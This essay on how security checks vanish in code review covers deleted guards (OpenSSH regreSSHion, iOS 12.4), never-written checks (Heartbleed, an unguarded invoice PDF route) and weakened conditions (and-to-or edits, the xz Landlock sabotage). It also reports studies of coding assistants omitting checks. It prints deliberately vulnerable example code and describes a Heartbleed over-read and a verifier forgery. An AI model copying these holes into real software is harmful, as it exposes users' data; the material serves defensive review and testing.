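Miller (2025), in *Inquiry about regreSSHion postmortem*, confirms that the error happened in the merge. He calls the bug his own mistake and says that two lines specific to the portable edition got lost in a diff of about 500 lines. Velvindron (2025), in *Fwd*, quotes the full message, in which Miller adds that other developers review nearly all substantial changes before he or a colleague commits them, but nobody reviews the merge again. De Raadt (2025), in *Followup on Inquiry about regreSSHion postmortem*, says that only two people manage the portable edition.

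The missing guard probably caused an early symptom. In May 2021 the developers stopped the handler from calling `sigdie` in one of sshd's processes, because the call could violate that process's sandbox. The commit summary, *branch master updated* (djm, 2021), doesn't mention the guard, but on systems where the guard had suppressed logging, its loss would explain the new violations. The developers fixed the process where the violations appeared, while sshd's privileged process continued to log from the handler.

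Red Hat Enterprise Linux 9 later showed how hard it is to cover every path. Its handler had a separate branch for the sandboxed process, with a comment against logging there, which matches the 2021 repair. The branch instead called a clean-up function that Openwall (2024) warned was also a problem in a signal handler, so a distributor who repaired only `sshsigdie` would leave a second unsafe path open. OpenSSH had dropped the branch after about nine months, but Red Hat's version still had it.

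Qualys contacted the developers on 19 May 2024, after noticing a public bug report about sshd freezing in the same handler. The fix followed on 6 June, more than three and a half years after the commit that removed the guard.

In a blog post analysing some of the project's commits, René Malmgren argued that somebody had probably reintroduced the vulnerability on purpose. Miller replied that it would make a poor back door, because the attack is slow, noisy and unreliable, and anyone who found the flaw could use it. The OpenBSD file and the project's usual order of work support Miller's account of a merge error. But a deliberate deletion could have produced the same diff, so a reviewer would do better to ask where the protection went than to guess at the author's motives.

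### Apple's iOS 12.4

In 2019, Apple reintroduced an iOS security flaw that it had already fixed. The flaw, CVE-2019-8605, let a malicious app run code with system privileges by exploiting memory that the system had released but continued to use. Apple fixed it in iOS 12.3 on 13 May. According to SC Magazine's *iOS 12.4 update reintroduced old bug enabling jailbreak for current devices*, version 12.4 reversed the fix on 22 July. On 18 August, a researcher known as Pwn20wnd released a jailbreak, a tool that removes Apple's restrictions, for fully updated phones. Tenable's *Apple iPhone and iPad Devices Vulnerable After Reintroduction of SockPuppet Flaw* reports that Apple restored the fix in iOS 12.4.1 on 26 August, after 12.4 had been exposed for five weeks.

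Sophos (2019) describes the reversal as accidental, but none of these accounts gives a cause. Tenable's *Apple iOS < 12.4.1 Use-After-Free (SockPuppet)* lists 12.4 as vulnerable but 12.3, 12.3.1 and the test version of iOS 13 as safe. That pattern would fit a fix that Apple had applied to some branches of its code but not to the one that became 12.4.

If so, there may have been no removed line to review. Reviewers could have read every change to the 12.4 branch without seeing the fix disappear, because the branch never had it. The loss would appear only in a comparison between 12.4 and the previous public release. SC Magazine says the original fix improved memory management, so it may not have been a check that tests a condition and refuses when it fails, but such a check could be lost between branches in the same way.

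### What exposes a deletion

A negative test can catch a deleted check even when nobody reads the diff. If the billing project already has a test in which a stranger requests invoice 17 and expects a refusal, that test fails as soon as the `if` and `raise` are removed. A project can find out whether it has such a test by removing the check on purpose and running the suite, which is the idea behind mutation testing. The protection is lost if the same pull request also deletes or rewrites the test, so a removed test that expects a refusal deserves as much attention as a removed check. Projects can require separate approval for changes to those tests.

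OpenSSH's guard would have been harder to test this way, because its loss mattered only when the signal arrived at a particular moment. If one attempt in 10,000 wins the race, a test that must win it to detect the flaw will succeed about 1% of the time with 100 attempts. A tool that checks which functions the handler can reach would be more reliable. LWN readers suggested static analysis and a C library that stops the program whenever a handler makes an unsafe call. Another reader objected that such calls are harmless if the program accepts signals only at safe moments, so either approach would reject some correct programs.

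A project can also list removed conditions separately from the rest of the diff, with any matching condition from the added lines beside each one. For the 2020 OpenSSH commit, the list would have had only three entries, because only three of the 132 removed lines begin a condition. One tests whether a message is important enough to log, and it reappears in the added lines with an extra term. Another tests for errors in a message passed between two processes, and it also reappears. The third is the guard, which has no match in the added lines.

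A program can produce this list for every merge, and three entries take much less effort to read than a 500-line diff. But the right list is easy to design once the fault is known, and this one would have helped only if somebody had looked at it. The project also has to record that code such as `@billing_scope` or a call to `prepare` protects something, because a program that looks for `if` and `#ifdef` will otherwise miss it. The program must also compare the right versions, which for a case like iOS 12.4 means each release and the one before it, whatever branches they came from.

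For each condition on the list without a match, the project can require the author to state where the protection now sits. For `get_invoice`, the author would need to name the function that now refuses strangers, list the other callers and explain what protects each of them. "Moved to the web handler" isn't enough. This requirement makes the author search for callers before the review begins and gives the reviewer specific claims to test. The request has to come from the list because an author like Miller, who didn't know he had dropped the guard, wouldn't think to provide the statement. A coding assistant can write a convincing statement without searching, so the reviewer should still open the functions it names or ask for a negative test on each path.

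Sometimes the program no longer needs the check. In June 2024 OpenSSH's developers moved the unsafe logging out of the signal handler and into another process, which could do it at a safe moment. Qualys warned that this fix might be difficult to apply to older versions because it was part of a much larger commit. For people who preferred to patch an older version, Miller (2024), in *Announce*, published a small patch that adds two lines to put a guard back around the logging code. The move to another process therefore protects OpenSSH 9.8 but not a patched 9.7, where deleting those two lines would reopen the flaw.

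## Never-written checks: finding a fault that has no line

When a developer never wrote a check, the diff contains no old condition for the reviewer to read. The new PDF route in the billing program might arrive as a new file, which Git shows as added lines only:

```diff
@@ -0,0 +1,10 @@
+from billing.render import render_pdf
+from billing.store import invoices
+from billing.web import app, file_response, login_required
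+
+@app.get("/invoices/<int:invoice_id>/pdf")
+@login_required
+def download_invoice_pdf(user, invoice_id):
+    invoice = invoices.find(invoice_id)
+    pdf = render_pdf(invoice)
+    return file_response(pdf, name=f"invoice-{invoice_id}.pdf")
```

Each line is correct on its own. The route accepts only whole numbers as invoice IDs, and `@login_required` blocks anyone who hasn't logged in. The function then finds the invoice, converts it to a PDF and returns it under a sensible file name. A reviewer who checks each line for errors will find none, yet all 1,000 users can now download invoice 17.

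### An argument in two steps

Since there is no faulty line to point to, the reviewer has to argue that a path reaches the sensitive operation unguarded and that the operation needs a guard there. Chen and colleagues require this argument for absence-type defects. In the PDF route, the path runs from the web address through `@login_required` to `invoices.find` and back to the user. Nothing in the ten lines compares the user with the invoice's owner.

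However, the ten lines can't prove that the path is open. `invoices.find` might return only the current user's invoices, or `app` might run a permission check before every route under `/invoices`. *Suspected Until Inspected* (Yang, Kang et al., 2026) lists several ways in which web applications restrict access to a stored object. The code may compare the caller with the owner, limit a database query to the caller's own rows, call a permission function, require a role, or rely on a check of a parent object, such as the project that contains the record. The check may also be in middleware, code that runs before the handler and may be registered in another file. The reviewer has to rule out all of these, because the code's author can refute the finding by naming one that works.

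Developers may also leave a path open on purpose. If the ten lines served price lists instead of invoices, they would not need an ownership check. Yang and colleagues found such cases in the results of FLINT, their tool for finding broken access control. For five whole applications, they read all 24 findings in one of FLINT's most confident categories, where a language model's output described an unguarded access and an attack. Eight were real or plausible faults, seven had little impact and nine were not faults. In five of those nine, the application allowed the access by design.

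### Where the evidence for a guard comes from

To show that the new PDF route needs a guard, the reviewer can compare it with existing code. The best comparison is `get_invoice`, a similar function that contains the condition the route is missing. But the reviewer has to know that `get_invoice` exists, and the author may reply that the two functions serve different people.

A recent security fix can also point reviewers to similar functions that may have the same flaw. *Characteristics, Root Causes, and Detection of Incomplete Security Bug Fixes* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) examines 26 Linux kernel security fixes that needed further correction. In some cases, the developer understood the flaw but overlooked similar code. One fix repaired several file systems but missed tmpfs, which keeps its files in memory and needed its own fix under a new vulnerability number. The researchers also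 searched for code that resembled earlier fixes, covering 1,615 kernel vulnerabilities, and found two more incomplete fixes. They finished this work in 2022. Their 26 cases, collected by searching for words such as "incomplete", can't show how common the mistake is.

A reviewer can check code against a written requirement, such as a protocol standard, a company policy or a sentence in the project's documentation, even if nobody has written a correct function to compare it with. "Customers may read only their own invoices" is specific enough to settle the case of the PDF route, while "Enforce access control" leaves the reviewer to decide what it means for this record and this user.

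A framework convention can make an omission easier to see. If a project's routes normally carry a permission decorator, a route without one looks odd, and a short program can list all the routes that lack it. The reviewer still has to know what the decorator checks. `@login_required`, for example, establishes who the user is but not what they are allowed to do.

The last kind of comparison point is a threat model, which describes the attackers a project expects, what they control and what they must not reach. It can justify a check when the new code is the first of its kind. For example, if the threat model includes someone who guesses passwords, the login function needs a limit on failed attempts, even if no other function in the program limits attempts.

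When none of these exists, the reviewer can show that every logged-in user can download every invoice, but not that this is wrong. It helps to ask whoever owns the billing policy and to have the answer written down, so that the next reviewer has something to compare the code against.

A similar function that is also unguarded is more misleading, because the reviewer might conclude that the project leaves this data open on purpose when both functions may have the same fault. Yang and colleagues examined endpoints (functions that handle outside requests) in the same files as 41 known vulnerabilities. They read all 37 of these neighbours that FLINT put in its top category. Twenty-four repeated the known flaw in their file, eight had real but minor faults and five were not findings. FLINT had already flagged these neighbours as suspicious, so the figures don't describe neighbouring code in general.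 Still, a reviewer who took any of those 24 as proof that the access was intended would have been wrong.

### Heartbleed: a requirement in the standard

The written requirement was precise in the case of Heartbleed, a flaw in the encryption library OpenSSL that became public in April 2014. OpenSSL 1.0.1 added a feature called the heartbeat in March 2012. One computer sends a short message and the other sends the same content back to show that the connection still works.

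A heartbeat request starts with one byte for the message type and two bytes in which the sender states the length of the content. The content follows, and then at least 16 bytes of padding. A request with the content "hello" and the minimum padding therefore takes 1 + 2 + 5 + 16 = 24 bytes and has a stated length of 5.

To build the reply, OpenSSL copied the stated number of bytes, starting at the first byte of the content. It never compared that number with the amount of data it had received. Suppose a client sent the same 24-byte request but stated a length of 65,535, the largest number two bytes can hold, instead of 5. OpenSSL would copy the 5 bytes of "hello", the 16 bytes of padding, and then the next 65,514 bytes in the program's memory. That memory could hold passwords, session cookies or the server's private key. The client could repeat the request indefinitely and get up to about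 64 KB each time.

The central part of the repair was a condition and a refusal:

```c
if (1 + 2 + payload + 16 > s->s3->rrec.length)
    return 0;
```

Here `payload` is the stated length and `rrec.length` is the number of bytes that arrived. For the request with the correct stated length, 24 is not greater than 24, so OpenSSL replies. For the other request, the left side is 65,554, so OpenSSL drops the message without answering.

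The code that read the length, reserved memory for the reply and copied the bytes was ordinary C. To show that a check was missing, a reviewer had to follow the length from the network to the copy and notice that nothing tested it on the way. RFC 6520, the standard that defines the heartbeat, already required the recipient to silently discard a message whose stated length was too large. A reviewer could have gone through the standard's requirements and looked for the code that implemented each one.

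Normal use did not reveal the missing check, because honest clients state the true length. A negative test for this check sends a request with a false length and confirms that the server does not reply. OpenSSL had supported the heartbeat for about two years before the fix.

### Two missing guards from 2026

In the run-identifier case from Chen and colleagues, the comparison point was in the diff, but the unguarded lookup was in an unchanged store of saved runs. The new endpoint, which resumes a paused run on an automation platform, checked authorization for the project. That check covered only the URL parameters, and the client sends the run identifier in the request body.

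The researchers tested this on a running copy of the platform. A user in one project could resume another project's run if they had its run identifier. The response exposed the saved conversation and the details of the tool calls the run was about to make. The user could also supply the decision that the run had paused to get from a person.

The reviewer had to follow the identifier out of the diff and into the store to show that the path was unguarded. The diff itself contained evidence that the store's lookup needed a guard, because related code there did tie its lookup to an owner. The authorization check on the route made the fault harder to see. A reviewer who checked only that the new endpoint followed the framework's convention would have approved it.

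The second case is from a gateway, a program that passes requests on to language models. Its developers had guarded two of eight methods against server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to fetch an address that the attacker can't reach directly. Here the changed lines contained all the evidence a reviewer needed. The two guarded methods showed that the developers knew of the danger and had a defence, so a reviewer only had to check whether each of the other six could fetch an address chosen by the client. But seeing two guards can give a reviewer the impression that someone has already dealt with the problem.

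These were among 12 previously undisclosed vulnerabilities that the researchers confirmed with working attacks. Nine of the 12 were missing checks. In four of those nine, the changed lines contained all the necessary evidence. One needed unchanged code from the same files, and four needed other files. The researchers selected candidates partly by whether there was something to compare them with, so these proportions may not hold for missing checks in general.

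One of the cases that needed other files shows why searching may not be enough. A pull request to a workflow platform left an authorization gap in eight functions that create or update records, in six files outside the change. No call or import distinguished these functions from others. They all called the same permission function, but a search for its callers returned 92 places.

### Comparing code with its peers

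Researchers automated the comparison of similar functions long before coding assistants existed. Suppose ten functions in the billing program return an invoice, and nine of them first check that the user owns it. A tool that groups the ten and lists the conditions each one tests will find that only the PDF route lacks this check. The tool doesn't need to know the billing policy, because it treats what most of the functions do as evidence of the rule.

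Chen and colleagues mention three systems that work this way but choose peers differently. RoleCast (2011) groups a web application's code by role and infers which checks each group should have, without a list of known checks. Chucky (2013) compares a function with others that are similar in meaning. APISan (2016) looks at every place where a program uses the same interface and infers which checks should accompany it.

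The method can't distinguish a mistake from a legitimate exception. A nightly job that emails every customer's statement has no user to compare with the owner, so it doesn't need an ownership check. The method also needs enough peers, and most of them have to be right. If the billing program had only `get_invoice` and the PDF route, just one of them would have the check, and a count couldn't show which was the mistake.

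Another problem is recognizing what counts as a check. Yang and colleagues describe a business-intelligence platform in which a user can delete a personal access token, a credential that lets other programs act for that user. Before deleting the token, the code calls a permission library to check whether the caller may delete a token with certain properties, and stops if the check fails. But it takes the owner's name from the caller's account instead of the stored token, so the token being checked always appears to belong to the caller and the check always passes. Anyone who learns the identifier of another user's token can delete it. A tool that looks only for a call to the permission library would count this function as guarded.

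FLINT tries to avoid this by dividing the work between a language model and a conventional program. The model, DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash, reads each endpoint and lists the stored objects that a client can select, the operations on them and the statements that seem to restrict the caller. The program then traces where the values in each statement come from. It accepts a check only if the check concerns this caller and this object, stops the request when it fails, and is strong enough for the operation. The model's output alone is enough to flag a possible fault, but not to rule one out. In the token case, the model cited the permission call as evidence that the deletion was safe, and the program rejected this because none of the call's values came from the stored token.

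Comparing endpoints with their peers is a smaller part of FLINT's design. The tool flags an endpoint if at least two related endpoints have a verified guard stricter than its own. This exposed a fault in Mattermost's boards plugin, where the functions for deleting and editing a comment check whether the caller owns it, but the function for restoring a deleted comment doesn't. However, among the 41 known vulnerabilities with neighbouring endpoints, the comparison found only one that the rest of the tool had missed.

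FLINT found 112 previously unreported vulnerabilities in 44 of 57 popular open-source applications. The researchers confirmed each one with a working attack that used two accounts with the lowest suitable privilege. In 40 of them the code had no check, and in 41 it checked the wrong object. Those 41 also lack a check if checks are counted by what they verify, because the code never tests the object that the user reaches.

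FLINT reports far more than these confirmed cases. On the five whole applications, it reported a definite finding for 385 of 786 request handlers (49%), so a person has to rely on its ranking. It can also miss faults, because it checks whether an operation is guarded only if the model lists that operation.

### How often coding assistants leave checks out

Published measurements give baseline rates for insecure code in general and for a few specific controls, but none of the measurements discussed here gives an overall rate for never-written checks.

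*The Security Decisions Claude Code and Codex Make* (Ong and Vikati, 2026) comes closest, because it names the missing controls. Ong and Vikati gave two assistants the same six tasks in order: login, file uploads, search, administrator controls, webhooks (messages that other services send to the application) and production settings. The prompts specified features and deliberately left out security advice. For example, the login prompt asked for registration that takes an email address and password, creates a user and returns a token. Claude Code ran Opus 4.6, and Codex ran a model that Ong and Vikati call GPT-5.4 in their summary and GPT-5.3 beside their code samples. Each assistant went through the tasks three times in each of two web frameworks, FastAPI and Next.js, for 12 sessions in total.

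None of the 12 sessions produced a limit on repeated requests. The application still accepted login attempts after 20 rapid failures. In nine sessions, it let a user register with a one-character password. None of the 12 sessions added the recommended security headers, though these are instructions to the user's browser rather than checks in the sense used here.

The results were much better for administrator access, which was one of the features in the prompts. Codex blocked ordinary users from the administrator pages in all six of its sessions. Claude Code did so in its three FastAPI sessions but was inconsistent on Next.js. This fits Ong and Vikati's conclusion that the assistants are literal and usually build what the prompt asks for.

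The study is small, and it comes from a company that sells such analyses. Ong and Vikati also point out that many companies limit login attempts at a gateway in front of the application, so a missing limit in the code isn't always a fault. A reviewer who sees only the application's code would have to find out whether such a gateway exists before concluding that login attempts are unlimited.

*PRECEPT* (Guo, Patir and colleagues, 2026) measured how often assistants write code that works but fails a security test. The study ran Codex, Claude Code and Qwen Code on short Python tasks, all using the Qwen3.6 model. Without any security guidance, 27.5% of the runs produced working but vulnerable code, with rates for the three assistants ranging from 25.4% to 30.0%. The researchers chose the tasks by starting from problems that all three assistants had already failed, so 27.5% isn't a rate for everyday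 work. The figure also includes vulnerabilities other than missing checks.

The more useful result concerns written requirements. The researchers repeated the tasks with guidance of increasing precision in the prompt:

| Guidance in the prompt | Runs with working but vulnerable code |
|---|---|
| None | 27.5% |
| One-line security reminder | 25.3% |
| All 218 OWASP secure coding principles | 24.2% |
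| Only the relevant OWASP principles | 23.3% |
| The relevant principle, restated for this class of code | 16.7% |
| What this particular task must check | 6.9% |

The differences in the second, third and fourth rows are too small to distinguish from chance. Yet in 19 of the 27 tasks an OWASP principle directly addressed the vulnerability, so the assistants had the rule and didn't apply it to the code. A reviewer who works from a general checklist may have the same trouble. The prompt in the last row isn't a practical remedy, because its writer must already know which check the task needs.

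Corrections did not carry over to new sessions either. When shown a failing security test, the assistants repaired the code in 85.7% of cases. In a new session, on a task with the same type of weakness, they wrote vulnerable code in 26.7% of runs, almost the same rate as without the earlier repair. None of them had saved the lesson to an instruction file or memory unprompted.

Guo and colleagues also cite an earlier result on feature requests in real projects. SWE-agent, an open-source coding agent running the 2025 model Claude 4 Sonnet, wrote working code for 57% of the requests, but the code was also secure for only 11.8% of all requests. Newer models may do better, and this figure too covers vulnerabilities of every kind.

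### When the assistant copies its neighbour

A coding assistant often reads similar functions before it writes a new one. This should help if those functions have the right check, but it may do harm if they lack it. Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026) tested both possibilities in *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* by keeping the task the same and changing only the surrounding code.

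For their more realistic experiment, the researchers took 20 places in five C and C++ projects where there had once been a memory-safety flaw. They removed the code at each place and asked an assistant to write it again from a short description, which mentioned neither security nor similar code. Code elsewhere in the project did a similar job, and it was mostly safe in one version of the project and mostly unsafe in the other. The researchers then built the program and ran an input known to trigger the original flaw.

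All five models wrote safe code less often when the similar code was unsafe, by an average of 35.4 percentage points. GPT-5.6 Sol's rate fell the most, from 91% to 42%. In one task from OpenSC, a set of tools for smart cards, it had to build a file path and add a two-byte identifier. A neighbouring file contained similar code for another type of card. GPT-5.6 Sol included a bounds check in the new code only when that file had one.

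The effect was much smaller in the other experiment, where three models wrote new web applications beside finished, unrelated ones. On average, insecure neighbouring applications lowered the share of new applications that were both correct and secure by 3.4 percentage points compared with having no neighbours, and secure ones raised it by 4.4 points. Insecure neighbours made little consistent difference when their weaknesses couldn't occur in the new application. The models seem to copy what fits the task, rather than writing less secure code whenever insecure code is nearby.

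The 35-point figure needs some caution because the researchers selected places that had a close counterpart elsewhere in the project and edited the counterparts by hand. All 20 tasks also concern memory safety, so the figure may not carry over to checks on who owns a record. The study did not cover deliberately planted examples, though the researchers note that an attacker could exploit the same mechanism.

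Telling the assistants to follow the repository's structure and style widened the gap between safe and unsafe surroundings for all five models in the C and C++ tasks, to as much as 55 points. This is an ordinary request, and code conventions were among the most frequent subjects in the instruction files Zarzycki surveyed. Warning the assistants not to bring in bugs from existing code narrowed the gap, as did a general reminder about security, but neither closed it. With the security reminder, GPT-5.6 Sol wrote safe code every time in safe surroundings and 68% of the time in unsafe ones.

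This kind of copying undermines the reviewer's best comparison point. If an assistant models a new function on an unguarded one, a reviewer who compares the two finds nothing out of place. Tools that compare peers have the same problem. In the example with ten invoice functions, only the PDF route lacked the check. If assistants copied it eight times, nine of 18 functions would lack the check, and no majority would reveal the fault. A written requirement or a negative test doesn't depend on the surrounding code, so it would still show that the check is missing.

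The assistants could often recognize the fault when asked, but they rarely volunteered a warning. Sun and colleagues went back to three of the models after they had written vulnerable code and asked whether it contained any bugs. On average, the models identified the specific flaw in 69.9% of cases. When asked separately why they had written the code that way, in 76.5% of cases they cited code elsewhere in the project that had a similar flaw. Claude Opus 5.5 mentioned the flaw in 11.8% of its final messages about vulnerable code and Claude Opus 5 in 5.9%, while the other three models never did. The researchers recommend a separate review after the assistant finishes, and advise developers to repair known flaws before giving an assistant new work in the same code.

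## Weakened checks: the same line with a looser condition

When a developer loosens a condition, the diff shows the old version directly above the new one, so the reviewer doesn't have to search the repository for something to compare. If `get_invoice` has a file to itself, the change from `and` to `or` looks like this:

```diff
@@ -1,7 +1,7 @@
 def get_invoice(user, invoice_id):
     invoice = invoices.find(invoice_id)
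     is_owner = invoice.owner_id == user.id
-    is_finance_admin = user.department == "finance" and user.is_admin
+    is_finance_admin = user.department == "finance" or user.is_admin
     if not (is_owner or is_finance_admin):
         raise Forbidden()
     return invoice
```

The hunk contains the whole function, and the `if` and `raise` are unchanged. A reviewer looking for a condition and a refusal will find both, and both still work. The removed and added lines differ by one word, and either would be a reasonable rule for some company.

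To judge the edit, the reviewer has to work out who passes the new condition but failed the old one. The old condition accepted people in both groups and the new one accepts people in at least one, so the edit lets in everyone who is in exactly one group. That adds 40 − 3 = 37 finance staff without administrator rights and 20 − 3 = 17 administrators outside finance, or 54 people. This set doesn't appear in either line of the diff. When a check is deleted, the reviewer can skip the calculation because everyone the old condition refused now gets in.

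### Ways to loosen a condition

Each condition in this table is one that a request must satisfy to get through.

| Kind of change | Before | After | Newly accepted |
|---|---|---|---|
| Comparison operator | `amount < 500` | `amount <= 500` | A refund of exactly 500 |
| Logical operator | finance `and` administrator | finance `or` administrator | The 54 people in exactly one group |
| Numeric bound | `amount < 500` | `amount < 5000` | Refunds from 500 up to just under 5,000 |
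| Lifetime | `link_age < minutes(15)` | `link_age < hours(15)` | Links between 15 minutes and 15 hours old |
| Exact match to prefix | `host == "pay.example"` | `host.startswith("pay.example")` | Longer names such as `pay.example.net`, which may belong to someone else |
| Exact match to wildcard | `exports/17.pdf` | `exports/*` | Every other file in the folder |
| Scope | `invoice.owner_id == user.id` | `invoice.company_id == user.company_id` | All the owner's colleagues |
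| Default | `settings.get("require_login", True)` | `settings.get("require_login", False)` | Anonymous visitors, wherever nobody has set the option |

The size of an edit is a poor guide to how much it weakens a check. Changing `<` to `<=` admits only one more amount, the limit itself, while changing `minutes` to `hours` makes a link last 60 times as long. In Python, replacing `re.fullmatch` with `re.match` means the pattern only has to match the beginning of the text, so a function that used to accept only an invoice number would then accept an invoice number followed by anything.

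The new operator doesn't show whether the check became looser either. Changing `<` to `<=`, or `and` to `or`, loosens a check if the condition lets requests through but tightens it if the condition refuses them. Suppose a developer tries to simplify the `if` line in `get_invoice` to `if not is_owner or not is_finance_admin`. The function now refuses everyone who isn't both the owner and a finance administrator, so nobody can read invoice 17. The correct rewrite uses `and` instead of `or`. The owner would soon report this mistake, but the 54 people who gain access from the other one have no reason to report it.

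Extra terms can mislead in the same way. If a program refuses a file whose stamp differs from the expected one, a developer might make this edit to prevent a crash when the stamp is missing:

```diff
-    if stamp != expected:
+    if stamp and stamp != expected:
         raise Forbidden()
```

The new line accepts any file without a stamp, even though it looks more careful than the old one. Hill (2026), in *Four Ways to Forge a Bundle My Own Verifier Calls Clean*, found comparisons of this kind in a verifier, a program that decides whether a package of evidence supports the results it claims. When Hill put false values in three of the stamps, the verifier rejected the package and reported each mismatch. When Hill deleted the same stamps, it accepted the package and still reported that the stamps agreed. Whoever submits a package decides whether it contains stamps, so they could turn off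 the comparison by leaving them out.

Hill's verifier also had a permissive default. It weighted each failed security test by severity and gave any severity label it didn't recognize a weight of zero. Hill capitalized the labels of the failed tests, changing "critical" to "Critical", which cut the package's vulnerability score from 10/22 (about 0.45) to zero, and the verifier accepted the false score. The default matched the verifier's specification, so a reviewer who compared the two would have approved the code. Hill doesn't trace either condition to a later edit, so both may have been loose from the start. But a developer could introduce the same fault into a sound check with a one-line change.

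### Testing at the changed boundary

Suppose the billing project has one negative test, which picks one of the 996 forbidden users at random, requests invoice 17 and expects `Forbidden`. If a developer deletes the check, the test fails whichever user it picks. If a developer changes `and` to `or`, the test fails only when it picks one of the 54 newly accepted users, a chance of 54/996, or about 5%. Testing ten random users would raise that chance to about 43%, and reaching 95% would take more than 50.

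Choosing the user deliberately can be worse, since the obvious stranger, who is in neither group, never exposes the change.

A boundary test uses a request that only just fails the condition. For a condition with two parts joined by `and`, this means a user who satisfies one part but not the other. An accountant without administrator rights is such a user. The correct function refuses the accountant and the `or` version doesn't, so this test catches the change every time. An administrator from engineering would catch it too, but other edits show why a project needs both tests:

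| Change to `get_invoice` | Accountant without administrator rights | Engineering administrator | Person in neither group |
|---|---|---|---|
| `and` becomes `or` | caught | caught | missed |
| Administrator condition removed | caught | missed | missed |
| Department condition removed | missed | caught | missed |
| `if` and `raise` removed | caught | caught | caught |

None of the three users owns the invoice.

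For a numeric limit, the boundary test uses the first forbidden value. If refunds must be below 500, the test requests exactly 500 and expects a refusal. This catches a change from `<` to `<=` as well as a limit raised to 5,000. A test that picks a random forbidden whole amount from 500 to 10,000 would catch the change to `<=` only if it picked 500, a 1 in 9,501 chance.

The test should contain the number itself. Developers often store a limit under a name such as `MAX_REFUND`, and a test that requests `MAX_REFUND` changes whenever the limit does. If somebody raises the limit to 5,000, the test requests 5,000, the program refuses, and the test still passes.

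Boundary tests also help when the looser condition is intentional. The developer then has to edit the test, and the diff shows the expected result for an accountant changing from `Forbidden` to an invoice. A reviewer can check that change against the billing policy without working through the logic of `and` and `or`.

### Mutation testing

To write a boundary test, someone has to think of the loosening in advance, but mutation testing generates the loosened versions automatically. *Mutation Analysis for Security* (Ennahbaoui and El Hajji, 2013) describes how a tool makes many copies of a program, called mutants, each with one small change, and runs the tests on all of them. A test kills a mutant if the mutant's output differs from the original program's. The mutation score is the fraction of mutants that the tests kill. In one of the paper's examples, the tool replaces `<` with `>` in a function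 that returns the smaller of two numbers.

Some mutants behave exactly like the original for every input, so no test can kill them. In the same function, the tool might replace the variable in a numeric comparison with another that always holds the same value. Someone has to remove these equivalent mutants before the score means much.

A mutation that removes a refusal imitates a deleted check, and one that replaces an operator or a number imitates a weakened check. Suppose a tool makes two mutants of `get_invoice`, one without the `raise` and one with `or`. If the only negative test uses a person in neither group, it kills the first mutant but not the second, so the mutation score is 1/2. Adding a negative test for the accountant raises the score to 2/2.

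A never-written check cannot be mutated this way. The PDF route has no ownership condition to alter and no refusal to remove, so a project's tests could kill every mutant of its existing checks while the route stayed open to all 1,000 users.

Iuliano, Carangelo and colleagues (2026), in *MuSe*, found this limit in a mutation tool for smart contracts, which are programs that run on the Ethereum blockchain. The tool can change comparison operators, logical operators and numbers, and it can also introduce particular vulnerabilities. One such mutation alters ownership checks. The safe version tests `msg.sender`, the account or contract that made the current call. The mutant tests `tx.origin`, the account that began the whole chain of calls. If an attacker lures the owner into using a malicious contract, that contract can call the owner's contract and pass the altered check. The mutation needs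 an existing check that uses `msg.sender`, so the tool could apply it to only 32,250 of 47,398 real contracts (68%).

Iuliano and colleagues also ran Slither, a program that searches contracts for known faults, on the mutants. It found about a third of the altered ownership checks (21,765 of 64,702), even though it has a rule for this mistake, but it found all 4,876 mutants that ignored the result of a low-level call. The gap may be due more to how the two rules work than to a general difference between weakened and absent checks.

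#### Deleting a verifier's refusals one at a time

Hill measured how well tests detected disabled refusals in the evidence verifier. The verifier rejects a package by adding a reason to a list of failures, and its code did this in 112 places. Hill disabled each in turn and ran 114 tests, along with a valid package that the verifier should accept and 16 deliberately altered packages that it should refuse. These checks detected the change in 37 of the 112 cases, or 33%.

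The 16 altered packages were meant to prove that the verifier could reject a package, but on their own they caught only 10 of the deletions. They could have caught at most 16, one per package, because deleting a check lets a package through only if no other check rejects it.

Hill had also found four ways to get a false package accepted, including the missing stamps and the capital letter. Fixing them and adding an altered package for each barely changed the score, which went from 37/112 to 39/119. The fixes introduced seven new refusals, and the tests covered two of them. Coverage of the original 112 stayed at 37. The regression tests guarded against the known faults but left most of the other refusals untested. Hill then wrote a test for each of the 75 unprotected refusals, and the score rose to 112/119, or 94%.

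One of Hill's early runs wrongly reported all 119 mutants as caught because two tests were already failing before the tool changed anything. The tool now starts only if the unaltered program passes its tests.

The study covers one program, which Hill wrote and measured alone. Some of the 75 refusals might have been impossible for any package to trigger, and a missing test for those would matter less. In a later version with 146 refusals, Hill excluded three for this reason and had tests that caught the deletion of each of the others.

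Even a perfect score on this measure leaves the other two forms mostly untested. One of Hill's four false packages got through because a necessary refusal had never existed, and a tool that deletes refusals couldn't reveal that. Hill's tool also didn't loosen any conditions. A test needs only one refused package to show that a refusal works, and that package may be as far from the boundary as the stranger who requests invoice 17. To protect its conditions, a project also has to mutate their operators and numbers. Hill cites an earlier study of 357 real faults in which 17% had no corresponding mutant among the usual kinds, so some loosened conditions would probably go undetected even then.

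### A stray dot in xz

In 2024, someone using the name Jia Tan put a backdoor into XZ Utils, a widely used package of compression tools. According to Tukaani's *xz backdoor* (2024), the backdoor was in the release files for versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1, which Jia Tan had created and signed. The code that triggered it was never in the project's public Git repository, but the repository did contain a smaller piece of sabotage, in a change that appeared to make a condition stricter.

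The change concerned Landlock, a Linux feature that lets a program restrict its own access to files. If an attacker used a malicious compressed file to take control of the `xz` program, this sandbox would limit the damage. Not every Linux system supports Landlock, so the build system tests for it before compiling `xz` and leaves the sandbox out if the test fails.

The old test only looked for a file named `linux/landlock.h`. Velvindron (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, quotes Jia Tan's message for the commit of 26 February, which explains that having this file isn't enough and that the new test also requires the necessary system calls. The new test tries to compile a short C program that uses them. sjw (2024), in the same discussion, reproduced the diff, which begins like this in abridged form:

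```diff
-    check_include_file(linux/landlock.h HAVE_LINUX_LANDLOCK_H)
+    check_c_source_compiles("
+        (three #include lines)
+.
+        void my_sandbox(void)
+        {
```

The dot on the fourth line isn't valid C, so the short program can't compile on any machine. The build system then treats Landlock as unavailable and continues without it. As sjw explained, this happens silently unless the person building `xz` has explicitly required the sandbox.

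The stated reason for the change was plausible, and the stricter test misled a reviewer about its effect. Tightening the condition for admitting a user increases protection, but when the condition switches on a sandbox, tightening it reduces protection because fewer systems get the sandbox. Here no system could satisfy the condition.

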